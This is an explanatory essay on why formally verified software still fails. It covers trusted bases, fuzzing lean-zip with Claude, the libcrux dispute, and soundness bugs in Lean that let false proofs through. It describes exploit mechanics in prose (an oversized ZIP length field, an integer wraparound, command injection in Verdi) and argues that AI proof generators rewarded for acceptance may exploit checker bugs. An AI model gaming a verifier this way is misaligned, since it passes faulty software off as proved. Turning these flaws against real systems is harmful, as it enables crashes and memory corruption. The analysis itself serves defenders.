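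For most everyday software, a team will probably do better to specify a few important properties than the whole program. The shop could require that a delivery charge is never negative, never exceeds a published maximum and never falls when a parcel gets heavier. A reviewer can check those three rules in a minute, and a proof would show that the program follows them for every possible order. A program could still satisfy all three and charge the wrong price for a particular postcode, so the shop would also need to test its price table.

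## What a proof takes for granted

A program with a valid proof and a good specification can still fail, because the proof relies on software and hardware it doesn't cover, called the trusted base. *On Formal Verification and a Bug in SP1 Hypercube* (Gunton, 2026) lists most of the following parts for one project, and other verified programs rely on similar ones.

| Part of the trusted base | What a fault in it could do |
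|---|---|
| Proof checker or solver | Accept a proof of a false statement |
| Tools that translate code into the prover's language, or proved code into a program | Make the proof describe a different program from the one that runs |
| Compiler and runtime | Turn correct source code into a faulty program |
| Unproved libraries and wrappers | Return values that the proof treats as impossible |
| Model of the machine | Make the proof true only of a machine that doesn't exist |
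| Hardware | Break the guarantee on the affected machines |

*The Trusted Computing Base of the CompCert Verified Compiler* (Monniaux and Boulmé, 2022) gives an example of a fault in an unproved library. Rocq treats every function as mathematical, meaning that the same input always gives the same result, so it accepts a proof that `f() = f()`. But if `f` is external code that returns a counter and adds one to it on each call, the two results differ when the program runs.

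A theorem can also contain assumptions of its own. Succinct's SP1 Hypercube produces cryptographic evidence that a program for a RISC-V processor ran correctly. The processor's JALR instruction has to set the last bit of the jump address to zero, but SP1 left this step out. The proof about JALR still succeeded because it assumed the address was already a multiple of four, which excludes every input that would expose the mistake. A standard set of RISC-V tests revealed the mistake, which made SP1 crash on some valid programs, though compilers rarely produce them.

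### The lean-zip experiment

Ten AI agents built lean-zip, a compression library written in Lean, and proved it correct on their own. One of the main theorems is that compressing any data smaller than a gigabyte and then decompressing it returns the original. *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, on kirancodes.me, describes how a researcher spent a weekend in April 2026 attacking the library.

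The researcher had Claude attack the library, after deleting the theorems and documentation so that Claude wouldn't learn that the code was verified and give up. Claude ran 16 fuzzers on six parts of the library for about 19 hours, totalling 105,823,818 runs. It also wrote 48 files by hand, modelled on known flaws in the standard zlib library. It found no memory errors in lean-zip's own code, but found two other faults.

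Both faults involve the number in a ZIP archive that gives a file's compressed size. The library's archive reader passed this number to Lean's file-reading function without comparing it with the archive's real size. A 156-byte archive in which this number was set to several exabytes therefore made the program run out of memory and crash.

The other fault was in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that every compiled Lean program relies on. To read *n* bytes, the runtime reserves *n* + 24 bytes, but it stores that sum as a 64-bit number, which wraps around to zero at 2^64. If the archive gives the largest possible size, *n* = 2^64 − 1, the sum is 2^64 + 23, which becomes 23. The runtime then reserves about 23 bytes but can write far more than that. The fault affected every version of Lean released up to then.

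Neither fault was in the proved code. No theorem covered the archive reader, and the theorems about compression assumed that the runtime worked correctly. A size check in the archive reader would have stopped input from triggering either fault through lean-zip. The agents had made the ordinary mistake of not checking untrusted input, in code just outside the part they proved.

The clean result for the proved code is encouraging, but it doesn't show how much the proofs helped. Lean's type system prevents many memory errors even in unproved programs, and these fuzzers tested mainly for crashes and memory errors, not wrong output.

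### The dispute over libcrux

The company Cryspen makes libcrux, a cryptographic library in Rust, and has verified many of its core modules. In November 2025 the cryptographer Filippo Valsorda reported that libcrux produced different keys and signatures from the same input on two kinds of ARM computer. According to GitLab's *GHSA-2cgv-28vr-rv6j* (2025), where a certain processor instruction was missing, libcrux used an unverified substitute that passed the wrong arguments. This corrupted the library's hashes, which led to wrong shared secrets and invalid signatures.

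In February 2026 the security firm Symbolic Software criticised Cryspen for fixing the fault without announcing it while advertising "the highest level of assurance". Symbolic Software's *On the Promises of ‘High-Assurance’ Cryptography* reports five further flaws in Cryspen's libraries. In one, a message counter could return to zero after about 4.3 billion messages and reuse values that must never repeat, which can let an attacker recover messages. In another, a verified decryption function correctly returned an error for a damaged message, but the unverified wrapper around it crashed the program instead of passing the error on.

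In Cryspen's reply, *The strengths and limits of formal verification*, Bhargavan (2026) wrote that the guarantees extend only to the verified modules, and that users also have to trust the proof system, the tool that translates Rust for it, the Rust compiler and the system libraries. Bhargavan added that nobody had yet found a bug in the verified code. The record of an older library that Bhargavan worked on supports the general point. In nine years its developers twice found errors in the specifications, while users more often found bugs in the 1,800 lines of unverified C that came with the library.

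Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs’ Verified Code* (2026), which calls Cryspen "CE Labs", describes two wrong formulas in a specification and a lemma stating that 12-bit values fit into a single bit. One of the formulas expands compressed numbers, and for a one-bit zero it gave 832 where the standard requires 0. The Rust code was correct here, so a proof that it matched the formula should have failed. The error went unnoticed because the build accepted the relevant proofs without checking them, even though Cryspen's status page listed the modules as fully verified.

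Symbolic Software sells audits and has published a rival to one of Cryspen's libraries, but its case rests on code and build files that anyone can inspect. Its argument about the proofs is persuasive. Bhargavan had written that every change must pass verification again before merging, but this means little for modules whose proofs the build skips. Skipping a proof has the same effect as a generator leaving an `assume` in it, although here people chose to skip the proofs, partly because some were slow to check.

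Bhargavan was right that most of the problems were outside the verified code. Kobeissi (2026), in *Verification Theatre*, counts thirteen vulnerabilities, nine in unverified code and four in specifications and proofs. One of the nine caused decryption failures in the Signal messenger. Kobeissi, who works at Symbolic Software, found the same types of failure in AWS's verified cryptographic library, so the problem isn't limited to Cryspen. According to flyingpenguin's *RustSec Integrity Breach Hides Dangerous Crypto Flaw*, Bhargavan later told The Register that "we did not do great with these advisories".

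### Where bugs in verified systems lie

The most careful evidence on this question predates AI-written proofs. *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) examined three systems that keep copies of data consistent across several servers and found 16 bugs. Eleven concerned the layer that connects the proved code to the network and the disk, three were in the verification tools and two were in specifications.

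More than eight months of searching revealed no mistakes in the protocols themselves, which are notoriously hard to get right. The faulty parts typically had only a few hundred lines of code, a tiny share of the trusted base. The study covered three research prototypes and didn't look for bugs in operating systems or hardware, so it can't show how common such bugs are.

Many of the bugs were ordinary. The system Verdi separated commands with spaces and line breaks but didn't escape those characters inside a client's data, so a client could hide a second command in a value, as in SQL injection, and the server would run it. The proved code then correctly copied the injected command to every server. Two of the faults in the verification tools were more worrying in principle, because they could let an incorrect program pass verification.

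### When a checker accepts a false proof

A soundness bug makes a proof checker accept a proof of a false statement. Since anything follows from a contradiction, one such bug can allow a "proof" that any program meets any specification. Monniaux and Boulmé cite an estimate of about one critical bug a year in Rocq, and Machine Logic's *Why is it all in the kernel?* mentions soundness bugs in Isabelle. Automatic solvers also have soundness bugs. TBTL's *A Soundness Bug in cvc5's Finite Field Split Solver* describes a misplaced overflow check that could have invalidated proofs about cryptographic programs.

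Until recently these bugs caused little concern. Monniaux and Boulmé argue that someone who wants a correct compiler is very unlikely to accidentally trigger a checker bug that lets a rare, wrong optimisation through. Their argument assumes an honest author, which a team can't assume when the author is an AI generator.

In July 2026, two checkers accepted a false proof. *Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576* describes how Ramana Kumar published a "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture in Lean, produced with AI assistance. The conjecture is that any positive whole number eventually reaches 1 if you repeatedly halve it when it is even and otherwise triple it and add one. Lean's kernel failed to check one part of a certain kind of type definition, and the proof contained an invalid expression there.

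Nanoda, an independent checker written in Rust, did inspect that part. But a week-old version had an unrelated bug and accepted the hidden expression. Kumar thinks the timing was a coincidence but can't rule out that the model had seen a report of the Nanoda bug. Lean's developers pushed a fix an hour after receiving a short version of the exploit.

AI helped find several other faults in Lean that summer. Release notes from Lean (2026) credit Patrick Hulin, working with GPT-5.6 Sol, with finding a kernel bug that a malicious proof could exploit if it ran in the same process as the kernel. According to *Safety Is Π₁, Provability Is Σ₁* (2026), a later version fixed three more soundness issues, which OpenAI had reported after AI-driven attacks on Lean. An OpenAI agent had turned one of them into two different proofs of a contradiction.

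Such bugs matter more when a generator searches hard for accepted proofs. With a soundness bug, the checker's false acceptance rate is no longer zero, so retrying is no longer harmless. An honest author has no reason to look for the bug, but rewarding a generator for acceptance also rewards it for exploiting the bug. The generator can reuse an exploit on every task, so the search is worthwhile even if it takes millions of attempts.

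For now, simple shortcuts such as `assume` are a bigger risk to a team than kernel bugs, because using them requires no search. The Collatz exploit depended on sending a definition directly to the kernel, so a rule against such code in submitted proofs would have stopped it. None of the reports describes a generator using a kernel bug to get a team to accept faulty software. Searching for kernel bugs also helps defenders, provided they find and fix the bugs first.

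### Time and memory

Most specifications describe a program's results but not its running time or memory use, and an attacker can exploit either. If a decryption routine takes slightly longer for some secret keys than for others, somebody who times many decryptions may be able to work out the key. A proof that the routine decrypts every message correctly doesn't rule out this attack.

Bhargavan's slides for the OpenSSL Conference describe a partial defence against timing leaks. A type checker labels secret values and forbids the program to compare them, branch on them, use them as array indices or divide them, because the time these operations take can depend on the value. The work on libcrux uncovered one such leak, called KyberSlash, which also affected other libraries. But the check covers only the source code, and a compiler may turn safe code into instructions that branch on a secret,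 so Bhargavan gives no formal guarantee about the compiled library's timing.

Memory can run out in proved code as well. In Verdi, a function that a tool had generated from proved code called itself once for each missing log entry. When one server fell more than 500,000 requests behind, these nested calls overflowed the call stack and crashed the server helping it catch up. The crash could then spread to the other servers, one after another.

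A specification can include such limits. The developers of IronFleet, another of the three systems, proved that every message fits into a network packet. Fonseca and colleagues found no bugs in IronFleet's connecting layer, though it also had the fewest unverified parts of the three systems. Proving a limit on a system's total memory use is harder, so they suggest measuring memory use in tests as a compromise.

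### Shrinking the trusted base and testing the rest

A small kernel leaves less code that can make a checker unsound. But checking can be slow, and the features that speed it up add code that must be trusted. Rocq's fast evaluators, for example, have had several critical bugs.

Lean has a similar option, `native_decide`, which trusts the results of compiled code. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) shows the risk. Given an enormous starting position, Lean's definition of a text-slicing function returns an empty string, while the compiled version returned the whole text. This contradiction allowed a one-screen "proof" of Fermat's Last Theorem. The kernel wasn't at fault. Lean listed an extra axiom among the proof's assumptions, so a team that accepts only the three standard axioms would have rejected it.

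**A second checker** helps only if it doesn't share the first one's bugs. Lean4lean, another checker for Lean, had the bug behind the Collatz proof because its developers had ported the affected code from the official kernel. A third checker, Nanoda, didn't have the bug, and an up-to-date copy would have rejected the proof. Lean's developers therefore advise anyone who may receive malicious proofs to keep Nanoda current.

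**Verified checkers** go further, but people still have to review their assumptions. *Zero-Trust Formal Methods* (2026) describes AI agents that built checkers for the results of automatic solvers. The agents' tests reported full success every time, yet four of six independent reviews found flaws. In one, two parts of the system read a specially written symbol differently, so a false result counted as proved. The reviewers looked for inputs that broke the agents' understanding of the format, which the agents' own tests had relied on.

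**Proofs about machine code**, like those for the fuzz-tested libraries and xv6, remove the compiler from the trusted base. They still depend on a model of the processor, which a team can test against real hardware. They could also help with timing, since any branch the compiler added is visible in the machine code. Cryspen plans to work with other researchers on this kind of analysis.

**Testing the unproved remainder** takes the least effort of these measures, and the bugs found in verified systems suggest where to start. Fonseca and colleagues built a toolkit that tests the parts around the proved code, for example by duplicating network messages and interrupting disk writes. It detects 13 of the 16 bugs they found. A team with a proved library should test its file readers, wrappers and fallback code in the same way, and run the tests on every type of processor the library supports.

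Proof checkers need such tests too, because they read files from untrusted authors. *Keel* (2026) presents a verified checker that runs inside the Linux kernel and decides whether to admit small programs, much like Necula's packet filters. Its developers fed 64 million altered proofs to Keel and to an unverified rival. Keel never crashed, hung or leaked memory. The rival had several bugs, three of which let a proof trigger an invalid memory read inside the operating system. The smallest such proof was 180 bytes.
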